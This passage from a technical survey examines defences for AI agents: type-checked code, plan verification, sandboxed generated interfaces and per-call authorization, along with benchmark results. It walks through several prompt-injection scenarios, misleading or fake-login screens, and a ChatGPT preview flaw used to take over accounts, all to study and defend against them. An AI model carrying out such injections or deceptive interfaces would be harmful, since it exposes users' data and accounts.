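The block returns a function that would read the file later, after the access should have ended. That function uses `fs`, so its type has to list `fs`. But `fs` exists only inside the block, so the type of `later`, which is outside the block, can't include it, and the compiler rejects the code. The compiler would accept a block that read the file and returned the text, because text carries no capability.

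The forwarders described earlier cut off access while a program runs, whereas here the compiler can verify beforehand that no code will use the access after the block ends.

All of this depends on complete capture sets, but some features of ordinary Scala can leave a capability out of them. A cast tells the compiler to treat a value as another type, and reflection finds functions by name while the program runs. TACIT therefore compiles the agent's code in Scala's "safe mode", which forbids casts, reflection and several smaller loopholes, and allows only safe library functions. Safe mode can't forbid exceptions, because even a division by zero raises one. An error message could carry a secret out of `map`, so the runtime catches exceptions and treats them as ordinary values, which it can wrap.

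TACIT sends printed output both to the agent's model and to a separate channel that only the user's terminal shows. Ordinary values look the same in both. If the code prints a classified value such as `count`, the user sees the number and the agent sees `Classified(****)`. The value stays wrapped in later turns of the conversation.

Odersky and colleagues consider this an advantage over CaMeL. A label can follow a value through a program, but it is lost once the value appears as text in a model's conversation. TACIT keeps classified text out of the agent's conversation. The disadvantage is that the agent can't see that text, so it can't notice for itself that a file is empty or in an unexpected format.

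### How TACIT did in tests

For their main test, Odersky and colleagues set up a software project with a folder of secrets that included API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 legitimate tasks with 10 injection attacks, for 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user asked for secrets outright or pretended to have a good reason, such as an emergency password change. They ran all 131 trials with two models, once with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and once as plain text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

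| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Secure trials, classified | 131 of 131 | 131 of 131 |
| Secure trials, plain text | 129 of 131 (98.5%) | 120 of 131 (91.6%) |
| Legitimate tasks completed, classified | 99.2% | 90.0% |
| Legitimate tasks completed, plain text | 83.3% | 88.3% |

The wrapper mattered most when the user asked for the secret, because that was when most of the leaks happened. Only 3 of the 240 injection trials leaked anything in plain text, all with MiniMax M2.5. The same model leaked secrets in 8 of the 11 trials with a malicious user.

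The perfect scores are reassuring, but the test was not very hard, because the wrapper always prints as asterisks and the test looked for secrets in what the agent printed. A harder test would have people look for mistakes in the compiler and the library, as Pydantic did with Monty. The higher completion rates in classified mode probably don't mean that wrapping data improves a model's work. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Sonnet's low score in plain text may be an artefact, since the model often ran out of turns or time and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

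They also tested whether writing typed Scala makes an agent worse at its job. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer-service conversations about flights and shop orders, three models each scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with Scala than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, in which an agent tries to fix 300 real software bugs, MiniMax M2.5 fixed 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% without it, a difference of five bugs.

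On τ²-bench, between 0.32% and 7.93% of programs failed on the first attempt, depending on the model and the subject, and those usually needed only one or two retries. Compilation takes less than a second once the compiler has warmed up.

These results show that models can write at least short programs in an unfamiliar language, despite long-standing doubts. They provide little evidence about the drawbacks of protecting data, because the customer-service tools returned ordinary, unwrapped values. They also don't show that types caused the gains. Odersky and colleagues credit the structured results and the compiler's error messages, but they compared Scala only with single tool calls. Letting the models write any kind of code might have helped as much.

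AgentDojo comes closer to testing the drawback, because TACIT wrapped most of the data there that an attacker could have touched. Across two models, one injection in 1,926 trials counted as a success. The attacker had put a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews of the one the user wanted to book. The agent booked the right hotel, and the injection counted only because the agent quoted the reviews to the user and AgentDojo treats any mention of the attacker's hotel as a success.

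TACIT's capture sets may account for only part of this protection. In the published interface for the banking suite, `sendMoney` doesn't require a capability, so the purity rule would apparently let code call it from inside `map`. The model is even told in its instructions that side effects there happen immediately. Much of the protection probably came from the wrapper, which kept the attacker's text away from the model that wrote the code.

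### The same idea in Haskell

`Classified` protects secrets, but types can also keep untrusted data out. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) does this in Haskell, a language whose types already separate pure functions from those with side effects. In its main example, an agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer-science papers. The function that writes to the file accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, and only the function that fetches entries from DBLP can create one. The model can sort and filter the entries freely, but if it invents one, its program won't compile.

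Their agents can also start other agents partway through a program. The compiler enforces the parent's rules on a sub-agent's code, so the parent can tighten those rules for the sub-agent but can't loosen them.

Garby and colleagues report that on AgentDojo's Slack suite, the Haskell agent completed 15 of 21 tasks without data flow rules and 8 with them, while CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions. Many of these tasks require data flows that a secure policy has to forbid, so a better compiler wouldn't let the agent complete them.

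### What the type checker can't rule out

TACIT guarantees limits on where data can go. But like the narrow tools in the orders example, it can't stop the agent from sending the manager a wrong total, because a program that computes the wrong total has the same types as the correct one.

A program can also leak secrets through timing. A pure function can't send anything, but it can run for a long time if a secret begins with a certain letter and finish quickly otherwise. Anyone who can time the program can then learn whether the secret begins with that letter. TACIT isn't designed to prevent this.

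The checks also don't cover external commands. When Scala code starts `git` or a build tool, the compiler cannot check what that program does. TACIT then relies only on a list of permitted commands, which has the same weaknesses as in any sandbox. Odersky and colleagues recommend adding an operating-system sandbox wherever security is critical.

The trusted base includes the compiler, the library, the runtime and the second model, which must not retain what it reads. Programmers can mark a library module as safe even though it uses forbidden features, and the compiler accepts the label without checking it. The core rules of capture checking have computer-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode still needs such a proof.

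The compiler can apply a type correctly and still miss a capability if the type itself is wrong, as happened with `Try` in Scala's standard library. `Try`, which TACIT relies on to contain exceptions, runs some code and stores either the result or the exception that the code raised. Its type marked the stored value as pure, but opening a stored exception raises it again, which uses a capability that the type had left out. Pham, Bračevac and colleagues (2026), in *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)*, corrected this by sorting capabilities into kinds. A `Try` value now keeps the capabilities for raising exceptions and drops the others, such as those for files.

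### LACUNA: code that the model writes as the program runs

In TACIT, the agent sits outside and submits code. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, from the same group, put the model inside the program:

`val total: Int = agent("add up the pending orders")`

When the program reaches a call to `agent`, the model writes Scala code to run there. The model receives the instruction, the type of result the program needs, and the surrounding code. The compiler checks the new code as if a programmer had typed it at that spot, so the code can use only the variables and tools available there. If `orders` is available and `customers` isn't, the model's code can't access `customers`. A programmer therefore grants authority by choosing where to put the call.

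The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. Suppose a balance is 100, and the program calls a model to write code that subtracts 50 and returns the new balance as a number. The model writes one line that subtracts 50 and a second that returns a sentence. In Python, the subtraction would run before the error in the second line was detected. LACUNA rejects both lines, so the balance is still 100 when the model tries again. This prevents some of the repeated actions that retries can cause, but code that compiles and fails later can still repeat its actions when retried.

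LACUNA also makes the `Classified` wrapper more flexible. In TACIT, the agent writes the function for `map` before any model has access to the secret. In LACUNA, that function can contain another gap, which a trusted local model fills with access to the text. The model might write one program for a contract with numbered clauses and another for one laid out as a table. The compiler still requires this code to be pure.

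This freedom makes the model's job harder. On τ²-bench, DeepSeek V4 Flash completed 76% of 392 tasks with LACUNA and 90% with ordinary tool calls. Zhao and colleagues describe the two as on par, which understates the 14-point gap. The compiler rejected 22.4% of the code this model wrote for the retail tasks. With the smaller Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, it rejected 89% on the telecom tasks, and the agent made little progress on most turns.

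AgentDojo allows a rough comparison with the two earlier systems. The percentages are tasks completed, and the last column counts successful attacks out of about 950 for each row:

| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel | Attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
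| Gemini 2.5 Pro | LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| o4-mini-high | LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |

CaMeL's 1.4% on the travel tasks is so far below its 74.3% with the other model that something probably went wrong in that run. Apart from that result, CaMeL did much better than TACIT on the workspace and Slack tasks with o4-mini-high, and about as well elsewhere.

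LACUNA let through seven attacks with Gemini 2.5 Pro, while TACIT let through none. Zhao and colleagues point out that the compiler enforces whatever access a gap has but can't check whether the task needed it. An attacker who steers the model into misusing a tool the task requires will also get past the compiler's checks.

### Proving a plan safe before it starts

CaMeL applies its policies when the program reaches each tool call, and by then earlier calls may have changed something. In *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), Meijer proposes checking the whole plan before any of it runs. The model writes all the tool calls as a structured workflow before it reads any data, a separate checker tries to prove that the workflow obeys the policy, and the host runs only workflows that pass.

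A policy can name a source of data and a place, or sink, that the data must not reach. For the orders example, it might say:

```
source: result of a query on the customers table
sink:   text of send_mail, if the recipient is outside the company
```

The checker looks for any path through the workflow from the source to the sink. Tools for finding security bugs, such as CodeQL, already search programs this way. The theft workflow contains such a path, so the host would discard it before querying anything.

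Checking the plan also catches an attack that planning first doesn't. The model reads tool descriptions before it plans, and a malicious description might include a fake company rule requiring a copy of every email to go to an outside address. The model may add that step to the plan, but the checker evaluates the step regardless of why it was added.

Meijer would also have the checker prove that a workflow does what the user wanted, which turns out to be slippery. Suppose a user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the agent has a tool that deletes every file matching a pattern. The obvious requirement is that both files are gone afterwards:

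foo.txt ∉ files ∧ bar.txt ∉ files

A workflow that deletes `*.txt` meets this requirement perfectly, along with every other text file in the folder. The requirement has to say what stays the same, too. For every file f other than those two:

f ∈ files after ⇔ f ∈ files before

Now the checker rejects `*.txt`. It also needs a rule that the tool leaves files that don't match the pattern unchanged. Without that rule, it couldn't prove that even the careful workflow is safe. Philosophers and AI researchers have called the problem of specifying what an action leaves unchanged the frame problem since 1969. Specifying this is easy for two files but much harder for a request like "tidy up my inbox".

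Meijer offers a design with worked examples and says that nobody has formally measured how planning this way affects an agent's performance. Nikolaou and colleagues have since built something similar on top of CaMeL. Their system turns the Python program into a diagram of its possible steps, then uses a standard verification tool to check rules such as this one, where AG means "at every step of every possible run":

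AG(send_message ⇒ recipient_trusted)

If a rule fails, the tool produces an example of a run that breaks it, and the privileged model uses the example to repair the program. Rules can also cover the order of events, which is hard for CaMeL because it checks each call separately. For example, a security team could require that a human give approval before the agent disconnects a computer, or that the agent eventually close every incident it opens. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven unsafe plans to test such rules. Their system caught all seven, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. They expected this result because they had chosen rules that CaMeL wasn't designed to express.

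Of CaMeL's 28 AgentDojo policies, 22 can be rewritten as rules to check before the program runs. The other six depend on facts that are unknown when the model writes the plan, such as who can open a shared file when the agent adds something to it, so CaMeL still has to check those while the program runs.

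## Temporary interfaces built by an agent

CaMeL and TACIT check programs that run once and return an answer. Agents also build small programs for people to use, such as a form, chart or dashboard for a single task. Suppose the clerk asks for a screen that lists the pending orders, with an Approve button beside each one. The screen stays open after the agent has finished, and it approves an order whenever the clerk clicks the button beside it.

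Many hosts are web pages, and a browser lets any script in a page read what the page shows and send requests under the user's login. The clerk didn't write the new screen and won't read its source, and the model that wrote it may have just read a customer's note. If the host inserted the screen directly into its own page, a script in the screen could read the clerk's other conversations or approve orders without the clerk's involvement.

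Hosts deal with this in two ways. They restrict what a screen can consist of, or they run it apart from their own page.

### Approved components

In the most restricted format, the agent sends no code. Google's *Introducing A2UI* explains that running arbitrary code from a model may be a serious security risk. With A2UI, an open format for agent-built interfaces, the agent describes the screen as data, and the host's app draws it with its own components. The project's website marks the *v1.0 Protocol Specification* (2025) as current, but in August 2026 the project's code page still listed version 0.9.1 as the production release and 1.0 as a release candidate.

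The app keeps a catalog of components it is willing to draw. The button for the second order could look like this:

```
{ "id": "approve_2", "component": "Button", "child": "approve_label",
  "action": { "event": { "name": "approve_order",
                         "context": { "number": 2 } } } }
```

The basic catalog has 18 components, including text, lists, sliders and date fields. It has no chart component, so a host has to add one to display charts. The catalog also lists functions that the app already contains, such as one that formats currency, and the agent refers to them by name. Each entry records who may call the function, and by default the agent can't call it remotely. `openUrl`, which opens a web page, runs only just after the user clicks or taps something.

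An approved component can still leak data. The basic catalog's Image component makes the app fetch a picture from a web address, so an agent could leak customers' names by putting them in the address, as it could with Cloudflare's page-fetching tool. A host can guard against this by loading pictures only from trusted servers.

Forms can also send data earlier than users expect. The app normally sends what a user types only when they press a button. But if a form checks a field with a function that runs on the agent's side, for instance to see whether an account number exists, the app has to send the field's contents to the agent before the user submits the form.

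Data and code are not sharply separated here. A2UI has `and`, `or` and `not`, and its text templates can call functions inside other functions. Its rules prohibit search patterns such as `(a+)+$`, which can take an extremely long time to match. *Generative UI (A2UI)*, part of the documentation for Google's Genkit framework, describes how the model writes short source text such as `root = Text("Sunny, 18C")`, which Genkit turns into A2UI messages.

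### Traid's language for screens

The Traid platform turns a prompt into a small browser app that people can save and share with a link. Traid's *We made the AI write in a language it can't break out of* (August 2026) argues that a tree of components becomes a language as soon as it needs conditions, so the designer may as well create one deliberately. Traid's language is a small Lisp based on Clojure.

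The clerk's screen might look roughly like this, with invented function names:

```
(column
  (text "Pending orders")
  (for [order (pending-orders)]
    (row
      (text (:number order) " $" (:amount order))
      (when (> (:amount order) 1000) (text "Large order"))
      (button "Approve"
        (on-press (approve-order (:number order)))))))
```

`column` and `row` arrange things on the screen. `for` makes one row per order, and `when` adds the words "Large order" to the two orders above $1,000. Layout and control flow use the same syntax, so a loop can appear among the items it produces. In a JSON tree, the designer has to put such logic into strings or invent special nodes. Traid reports that its programs need a fraction of the tokens, but gives no figures.

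An app in this language can't call the browser's `fetch`, because the interpreter doesn't connect the language to the JavaScript underneath. As in PTC-Lisp, an app can call only functions that the host has registered, such as `approve-order`.

Apps also store data through registered functions. A counter app might call a host function to add one to the value named `count`, without specifying where that value is stored. A part of the host called the state provider determines that. One provider keeps the value on the user's device, another syncs it to the user's account, and a third keeps a single copy for everyone who has the app open. Changing a setting on the saved app turns a private counter into a live shared one without changing the program. With the shared provider, adding a message to a list updates every viewer's screen.

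Traid contrasts this with JavaScript apps, which tend to write directly to the browser's storage and would have to be regenerated. That is a fair description of typical JavaScript, but the host functions matter more than the language. A Dynamic Worker whose only binding was a similar storage object could also move from private to shared without changes.

As with PTC-Lisp, models write most of the language correctly but try to use some Clojure features it lacks. When told that a feature was unsupported, models wrote the same thing again, so Traid's error messages now give the valid form instead. Traid found worked examples more useful than written instructions, and has a stronger model prepare sets of them in advance. Agents building a drawing app and agents building a dashboard get different examples.

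Traid recommends against a custom language for apps that need many existing libraries, and acknowledges that several ways of isolating JavaScript would also work. It has published no attack tests, and given the escapes from Monty, it would be sensible to also run Traid's interpreter inside a browser frame.

### JavaScript in a browser frame

A frame is a web page displayed inside another page. Browsers separate pages by origin, roughly the site they came from, so a script in a frame from a different origin can't read the surrounding page or its cookies. The host can restrict the frame further with sandbox settings and a content security policy, a list of the addresses the frame may contact. Within those limits, the interface can do almost anything a web page can, including run games and display maps and animated charts.

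MCP Apps lets tool servers supply screens that appear in frames. Model Context Protocol (2026) announced it in January as the first official MCP extension, already supported by ChatGPT, Claude, Goose and Visual Studio Code. *SEP-1865* (Salomon, Yosef and colleagues, 2025) sets out the rules, and Model Context Protocol's *MCP Apps* lists the version of January 26, 2026 as stable, with a successor in draft. The server's author writes the HTML beforehand, so the host can inspect the screen before showing it. The model only decides when to call the tool. ChatGPT's HTML previews also use a frame, but they can show a page the model has just written.

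If the host is a web page, it must load an intermediate frame from another origin and put the screen, called the view, in a second frame inside that one. The view can contact only outside addresses that the server has declared, and the host may block some of these but may not add others. These limits help if an attacker compromises the view. They do little against a malicious server, which can declare its own address and also receives whatever the view sends it through tool calls.

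A view can also get around the network restriction by asking the host to open a link whose address contains data. It can add text to the model's context or post a message to the chat in the user's role. Salomon and colleagues let hosts ask for consent before posting the message but don't require it, so a view could deliver a prompt injection that looks as though the user typed it.

But MCP Apps can keep untrusted text away from the model. A tool can return one result for the model and a fuller one only for the view. The clerk could then read the customers' notes on the screen while the model received only order numbers and amounts.

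Veneer, a product in private beta, uses a frame with no network access and a short list of registered actions. In its example, a generated screen can create and update tasks but can't delete them, because nobody registered a delete action. But if the update action accepts any text, a screen could still replace every task with a blank one.

### WebAssembly components without frames

Frames are awkward to combine because each is a separate page. *Capability-Based Generative User Interfaces Using the WebAssembly Component Model*, a demonstration shared with an online programming community, instead loads components into one web app. Each component imports only the resources the host allows, such as a clock or a channel for reporting events. It has no direct access to the page, so it returns a description of what to show, and the host removes anything dangerous from the HTML and styling before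 drawing it.

The protection depends on that cleaning step, because the host draws the result in its own page with its own authority. In the discussion under the demonstration, a reader who had used an AI system to look for gaps reported that the filter checked link addresses stored as text but skipped those stored as lists, so a component could have run a script in the host's page. The developer replied that the design allows for safety and needs a couple more rounds of polishing. The reader liked the idea but still expected to feel safer with frames. The developer compared frames to mini-apps talking "through a json straw".

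| Format | What a screen can do | What has to work correctly |
|---|---|---|
| Approved components | Show whatever the catalog provides | The app's components and functions |
| Small language | Also use loops, conditions and its own logic | The interpreter and the host functions |
| JavaScript in a frame | Almost anything a web page can | The browser, the frame's settings and the message handling |
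| WebAssembly components | Any computation, but only HTML that the host accepts | The runtime and the HTML filter |

### From a button press to a host function

Suppose the clerk's screen is an MCP Apps view, supplied by the company's order server, and the clerk presses Approve beside order 2.

1. The view's script creates a request to call the tool `approve_order` with the number 2.
2. The browser passes the request to the intermediate frame, which forwards it to the host's page.
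3. The host checks permission. It confirms that the request is valid and that the tool's settings allow calls from apps, and otherwise rejects it.
4. The host may also apply its own policy or ask the clerk to confirm.
5. The host forwards the request to the order server. The server should check whether the clerk's account may approve this order before it does so.
6. The result goes back to the view, which marks the order as approved.

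The required check in the third step is fairly weak. A tool is available to both the model and the view unless the server's author restricts it, so a screen meant only to display orders may also be able to approve them. The check also applies to the tool as a whole, so a view that needs to approve order 2 can also approve order 3 unless the host or the server has a narrower rule.

The request also doesn't prove that anyone pressed a button, because the view's script can send it as soon as the screen opens. A2UI's rule for `openUrl` is stricter because the app itself verifies that the user has just acted.

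In A2UI, the Approve button in the earlier example sends the agent an event named `approve_order` with the number 2, instead of calling a tool. The agent then decides what to do, and the host checks any tool call the agent makes as usual. This gives the screen less authority but puts a model between the click and the action. In Traid, the interpreter looks up `approve-order` in the host's table and calls the function, which has to make any further check itself.

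### The channel between a frame and its host

A frame that couldn't communicate would be safe but not very useful, so browsers provide a function called `postMessage`, which sends data between pages of different origins. The browser labels each message with its origin, but the receiving page's own code, which runs with the user's login, has to determine which messages to trust.

In October 2026, a flaw in ChatGPT's HTML previews let a preview run its own code in the main ChatGPT page. *Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026) describes how researchers at Parameter Labs found it. The frame that held the preview did stop its code from reading the main page. But *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts* (Willison, 2026) explains that the main page contained code for another feature, which accepted messages from any frame and used their contents to change the page. A preview could exploit that code, though the attack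 took several further steps.

An attacker could put such a preview in a ChatGPT conversation and share the link. Anyone who opened it while logged in would run the attacker's code with access to their account. The researchers confirmed that the code could list the victim's conversations, read a private one and send its contents to an outside server. OpenAI fixed the flaw on October 26 and paid a $5,000 bounty, which Willison thought a bit low for such a serious flaw. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reported another preview flaw in November, also fixed, that let crafted content bypass restrictions and extract chat data.

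The October flaw made ChatGPT's page a confused deputy. The preview had no access to the victim's account, but the page did, and it acted on a message from the preview. Isolating the preview's frame more strictly wouldn't have helped, because the message used a channel that was supposed to be open.

Hosts can make the channel safer by checking which frame sent each message, accepting only a short list of requests, and never inserting a message's contents into the page as HTML. Salomon and colleagues require structured messages and tell hosts to validate them and log the requests that views make. However, their own short example of a view numbers its requests from 1 upward and accepts any reply with the right number without checking the sender. The example is meant to show that a view doesn't need a special library, but developers often copy such examples.

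### Screens that mislead the user

A screen can mislead the user even if every check works. Suppose the customer's note leads the model to label a button "Approve order 1" but attach the number 2 to it. When the clerk presses the button, the host confirms that the view may call `approve_order`, and the server confirms that the clerk may approve orders and then approves order 2.

A fake login form supplied by a malicious tool server can steal a password without an internet connection. The view that displays the form can send the password to that server with a permitted tool call.

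Researchers at Eye Security tried making a login screen in the shareable canvases of AI chat services. Gemini warned viewers that another person had created the content, and the researchers suspected that most people would then close the chat. They moved on to ChatGPT. Its own login screen looked "straight out of the 90s", so they pasted in the HTML that Gemini had written.

A warning like Gemini's is useful because it comes from the host. Salomon and colleagues likewise recommend that hosts clearly mark the edges of a view, though a view can request no border or a full-screen display. According to Model Context Protocol's *MCP Apps Overview*, the host ultimately decides how to display views.

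It is harder to show where an agent's part of the screen begins and ends when it is built from approved components. Google presents the native feel of A2UI screens as an advantage, but it also makes it harder for users to tell which parts an agent wrote. A2UI also lets the agent give a button one visible label and another for screen readers, which must announce the second. This is meant to help blind users, but a misleading agent could show "Pay" and have the screen reader announce "Cancel".

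For actions that matter, the host should ask for confirmation in its own window, outside the generated screen, and base the question on the actual request. A clerk who reads "Approve order 2, for $450?" would notice the false label, provided that the host looks up the amount itself instead of taking it from the screen.

### When an interface closes or someone shares it

When the user closes an MCP Apps view, the host notifies the view and should wait for a reply so that the view can save its work. The host then removes the frame and stops listening to it, which ends the view's access through the host. The host needs a deadline for the reply, because a view that never replied could delay its own removal. Closing the view doesn't remove text it has already added to the model's context or revoke the tool server's own access to the user's account.

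A saved app has no such obvious end. If the clerk opens the orders screen again next month, the host shouldn't automatically reuse last month's permissions.

It also matters whose authority a shared app uses. If the clerk sends a colleague the orders screen and `approve-order` still uses the clerk's account, anyone with the link can approve orders. The host should share the program without its permissions and connect its functions to the account of whoever opens it. But then a malicious author can make the program act with the recipient's authority, as happened in the ChatGPT attack. So a shared app should start without access to the recipient's data or accounts, and the recipient should choose what to allow.

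Traid's setting for shared storage needs similar care. The app can't detect which state provider it has, so the host has to warn people that anything they type may appear on everyone else's screen once the app is shared. The host also has to decide whether entries saved privately become visible when the setting changes. The state provider has to enforce rules such as "only the clerk may delete entries", since the model may have written the app before anyone planned to share it.

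## Authorizing each tool call and withdrawing access afterwards

When the host asks the clerk to confirm an approval, the clerk decides on one call, based on its actual arguments. But an agent may make hundreds of calls in a task, and nobody will read that many questions carefully. Several designs from 2025 and 2026 therefore use an ordinary program to compare each call with a policy and, if the policy allows the call, grant access for a few seconds or for one step of the task.

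### From a proposed call to an executed one

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, place such a program between an agent and its MCP tool servers. A policy author writes a rule for each tool. For the email in the orders example, a rule modeled on their banking policy might look like this:

```
grant email_total {
  action: write
  resource: "mail/outgoing"
  intent: [report_total]
  trust: >= 0.8
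  requires: [read_pending_orders]
  ttl: 30s
  budget: 1
  bound_params: [recipient]
}
```

The rule allows one email, within 30 seconds, to report a total. When the agent proposes the email, AGENTCAP handles the call like this:

1. The model writes the call, with a recipient and some text, and picks a purpose from the rule's list.
2. A policy engine runs seven checks. The agent must not be locked out after earlier trouble, and the tool must be in the policy. The recipient must come from an acceptable source, and the purpose must be on the list. The agent needs a high enough trust score and a valid permission to read pending orders. Finally, the new permission must not complete a forbidden combination, such as reading customer data and sending outside mail in the same session.
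3. If every check passes, the engine issues a token, a short piece of signed data that names the agent, session, action, resource and purpose.
4. A gateway verifies the signature. It also checks that the token hasn't expired, that nobody has revoked it, that it has a call left, and that the right agent is using it for the right action.
5. The gateway forwards the call and returns the result. If a check fails, the agent gets the reason and can try something else.

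No language model takes part in steps 2 to 4. Issuing a token takes about 67 microseconds and verifying it about 80.

The token is a string of bits that acts as a capability, so a model could leak it. Each token is tied to one agent and one session, which makes a stolen copy useless elsewhere. But the token doesn't record the recipient, so the host must send exactly the call that the engine checked. Sandlock's supervisor faced the same problem when a program changed an address after approval.

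Declaring a purpose only prevents the agent from using a token issued for one purpose to do something unrelated. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao acknowledge that this protection is limited, because the model chooses the purpose and an injected instruction can influence the choice.

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) had already checked each call against rules about tool names and arguments. A language model drafts the rules from the user's request and proposes changes as the agent learns more. Suppose a user asks an agent to do whatever Alice's to-do email says. At first, the agent may only search for that email. The email asks for a summary of recent messages on Slack, so the model proposes allowing the agent to read mail and post messages. A solver, a program that can compare which calls the old and new rules allow, finds that this would expand the agent's access, so the change needs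 approval. When the agent learns that the user's Slack name is `alice`, the model proposes limiting posts to that name. This change takes effect automatically because it narrows the agent's access.

If one of the recent messages then tells the agent to forward the inbox to a stranger, it might trick the model into proposing a rule that allows this. The solver would again detect that the rule expands the agent's permissions, and whoever reviews expansions could reject it. On AgentDojo, Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0%, and only 6% of the policy updates needed approval.

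### When the attacker chooses the recipient

Permission to send email does not settle whether an agent should send a particular message. In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) examined the public code of three widely used toolkits: LangChain, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which handles payments. All three let developers limit which tools or actions an agent has, but by default none of them checks the values in a call against a policy before running it.

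Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a tool that changes the account receiving a merchant's payments, connected to a mock payment system. When a prepared model output called the tool with an attacker's account number, LangChain made the change. The agent was supposed to have the tool, and the account number had the right type. ScopeGate, a checker whose policy listed the merchant's own account as the only valid one, refused the identical call. Developers can write such a check themselves, so the test shows only that LangChain does not make it by default.

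An early version of ScopeGate rejected a payment only if the amount was greater than a limit. This let through a payment of NaN ("not a number"), a special numeric value that isn't greater than anything. The corrected version accepts an amount only if it is a finite number between zero and the limit. Mellafe Zuvic also had a model attack ScopeGate while seeing the reason for each refusal. ScopeGate blocked all 29 of the model's unauthorized calls.

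A fixed list works less well when the recipients depend on what the agent reads, as with the emails about late orders. In that case, the host can check where each address came from.

### Tracing an argument to its source

CaMeL can label every value because its interpreter computes the values itself. In an ordinary agent, a model that has read both the clerk's request and the customers' notes writes the arguments, so the host has to infer where each argument came from by examining the argument.

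AGENTCAP does this for the arguments listed in `bound_params`. The policy labels the clerk's request and certain fields in tool results as trusted, and free text such as order notes as untrusted. The host records the values from each source and rejects a protected argument if its value appears only in untrusted sources. If the manager's address appears in both the clerk's request and a note, the agent can still use it.

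*The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (2026) sets out a similar procedure in more detail. The host looks first for an exact match in the user's input, then in earlier tool results, and then for a clear transformation of a known value. If the source is still uncertain and the argument determines something important, the host treats it as untrusted. In the orders example, that gives these results:

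| Recipient in the call | What the host finds | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| Address in the clerk's request | Trusted source | Allow |
| Address in the customers table | Source the policy labels as trusted | Allow |
| Address only in an order's note | Untrusted source | Refuse |
| Address with no clear match | Unknown source | Refuse |

*Agent-Sentry* (2026) also treats unidentified sources as hostile.

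The third row stops the original theft but, like CaMeL's policy, also blocks a customer's genuine new address. The fourth can block an agent that correctly works out an address from a person's name and the company's usual format. All of this depends on the labels. For example, if customers can edit their own entries in the customers table, the second row treats text that an attacker may have written as trusted.

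*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) combines two kinds of check. Before each call, the host freezes the arguments and matches them against the values it has seen, building a graph of where data came from and where it went. The first check searches this graph for a path from untrusted or secret data to a harmful effect. The second compares the call's effects with permissions derived only from the user's authenticated request. Its nine conditions cover, among other things, the operation, the arguments, confidentiality, the number of calls left and whether the permission is still current.

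PACE also searches arguments for disguised secrets. It recognizes common hashes and several standard encodings, such as base64 and hexadecimal, but misses paraphrases, translations and short fragments. It can also produce false positives, because short values turn up by coincidence. For example, if someone had marked order amounts as confidential, "450" in a street address could match the amount of the second order.

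A deeper limitation of matching values is that it doesn't check what led the agent to choose a value. Suppose the clerk's request mentions both the manager's address and a courier's, and asks the agent to send the total to the manager, but a customer's note tells the agent to send it to the courier instead. If the agent follows the note, AGENTCAP's source check would accept the courier's address because it appears in the clerk's request.

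*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) proposes tracking what could have influenced each argument in a tool call, as well as where its characters came from. An argument counts as untrusted if untrusted text might have affected how it was chosen. This rule alone would block a lot of useful work, so trusted code can release a narrow value from untrusted text for one purpose. For example, it might extract a file path from an error log, check that the file is in the project, and allow the agent to use the path as the file to edit. The log's contents still couldn't determine which tool the agent used or mark a change as approved. In 400 coding episodes, no unauthorized call got through. The agent safely completed the task in 231 of them, a figure that also depends on how well the model wrote code.

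### What the checks stopped, and what they cost

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested AGENTCAP on all of AgentDojo, including 949 combinations of task and attack, and on 1,054 attacks from a similar benchmark, InjecAgent. They ran two models once each, with and without the checks:

| Benchmark and model | Successful attacks, without → with | Tasks completed under attack, without → with |
|---|---|---|
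| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.6% → 5.1% | 73.6% → 74.9% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.2% → 0% | 75.7% → 75.0% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.2% → 8.6% | 74.1% → 69.9% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 12.0% → 0% | 73.0% → 69.9% |

When nobody was attacking, AGENTCAP cost GPT-4o three of the 97 AgentDojo tasks and GPT-5.4 seven.

Some of the attacks that still worked on GPT-4o only needed the model to write something in its answer, which a check on tool calls can't prevent. Others used an argument that the policy didn't protect, or arrived through a field that nobody had labeled. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao describe the last two kinds as gaps in the policy rather than failures of enforcement, which is fair, though the harm to the victim is the same.

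The drop in completed tasks was small, but it would probably be somewhat larger in practice. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao froze their policies before the tests, but they wrote them after reading the benchmark's tools and task descriptions, and a company can't read its employees' requests in advance. The tests also didn't include attackers who adapt to the checks.

The same caution applies to the comparison between AGENTCAP and Progent. With GPT-4o, both systems let through about the same number of attacks, but Progent completed only 68.0% of tasks without attacks and 59.6% with them, compared with 78.4% and 74.9% for AGENTCAP. GPT-4o wrote Progent's rules during each task, and these often allowed only the values it had predicted, so they blocked legitimate calls. People who could see the tasks wrote AGENTCAP's rules, so the comparison is partly between two ways of writing policies.

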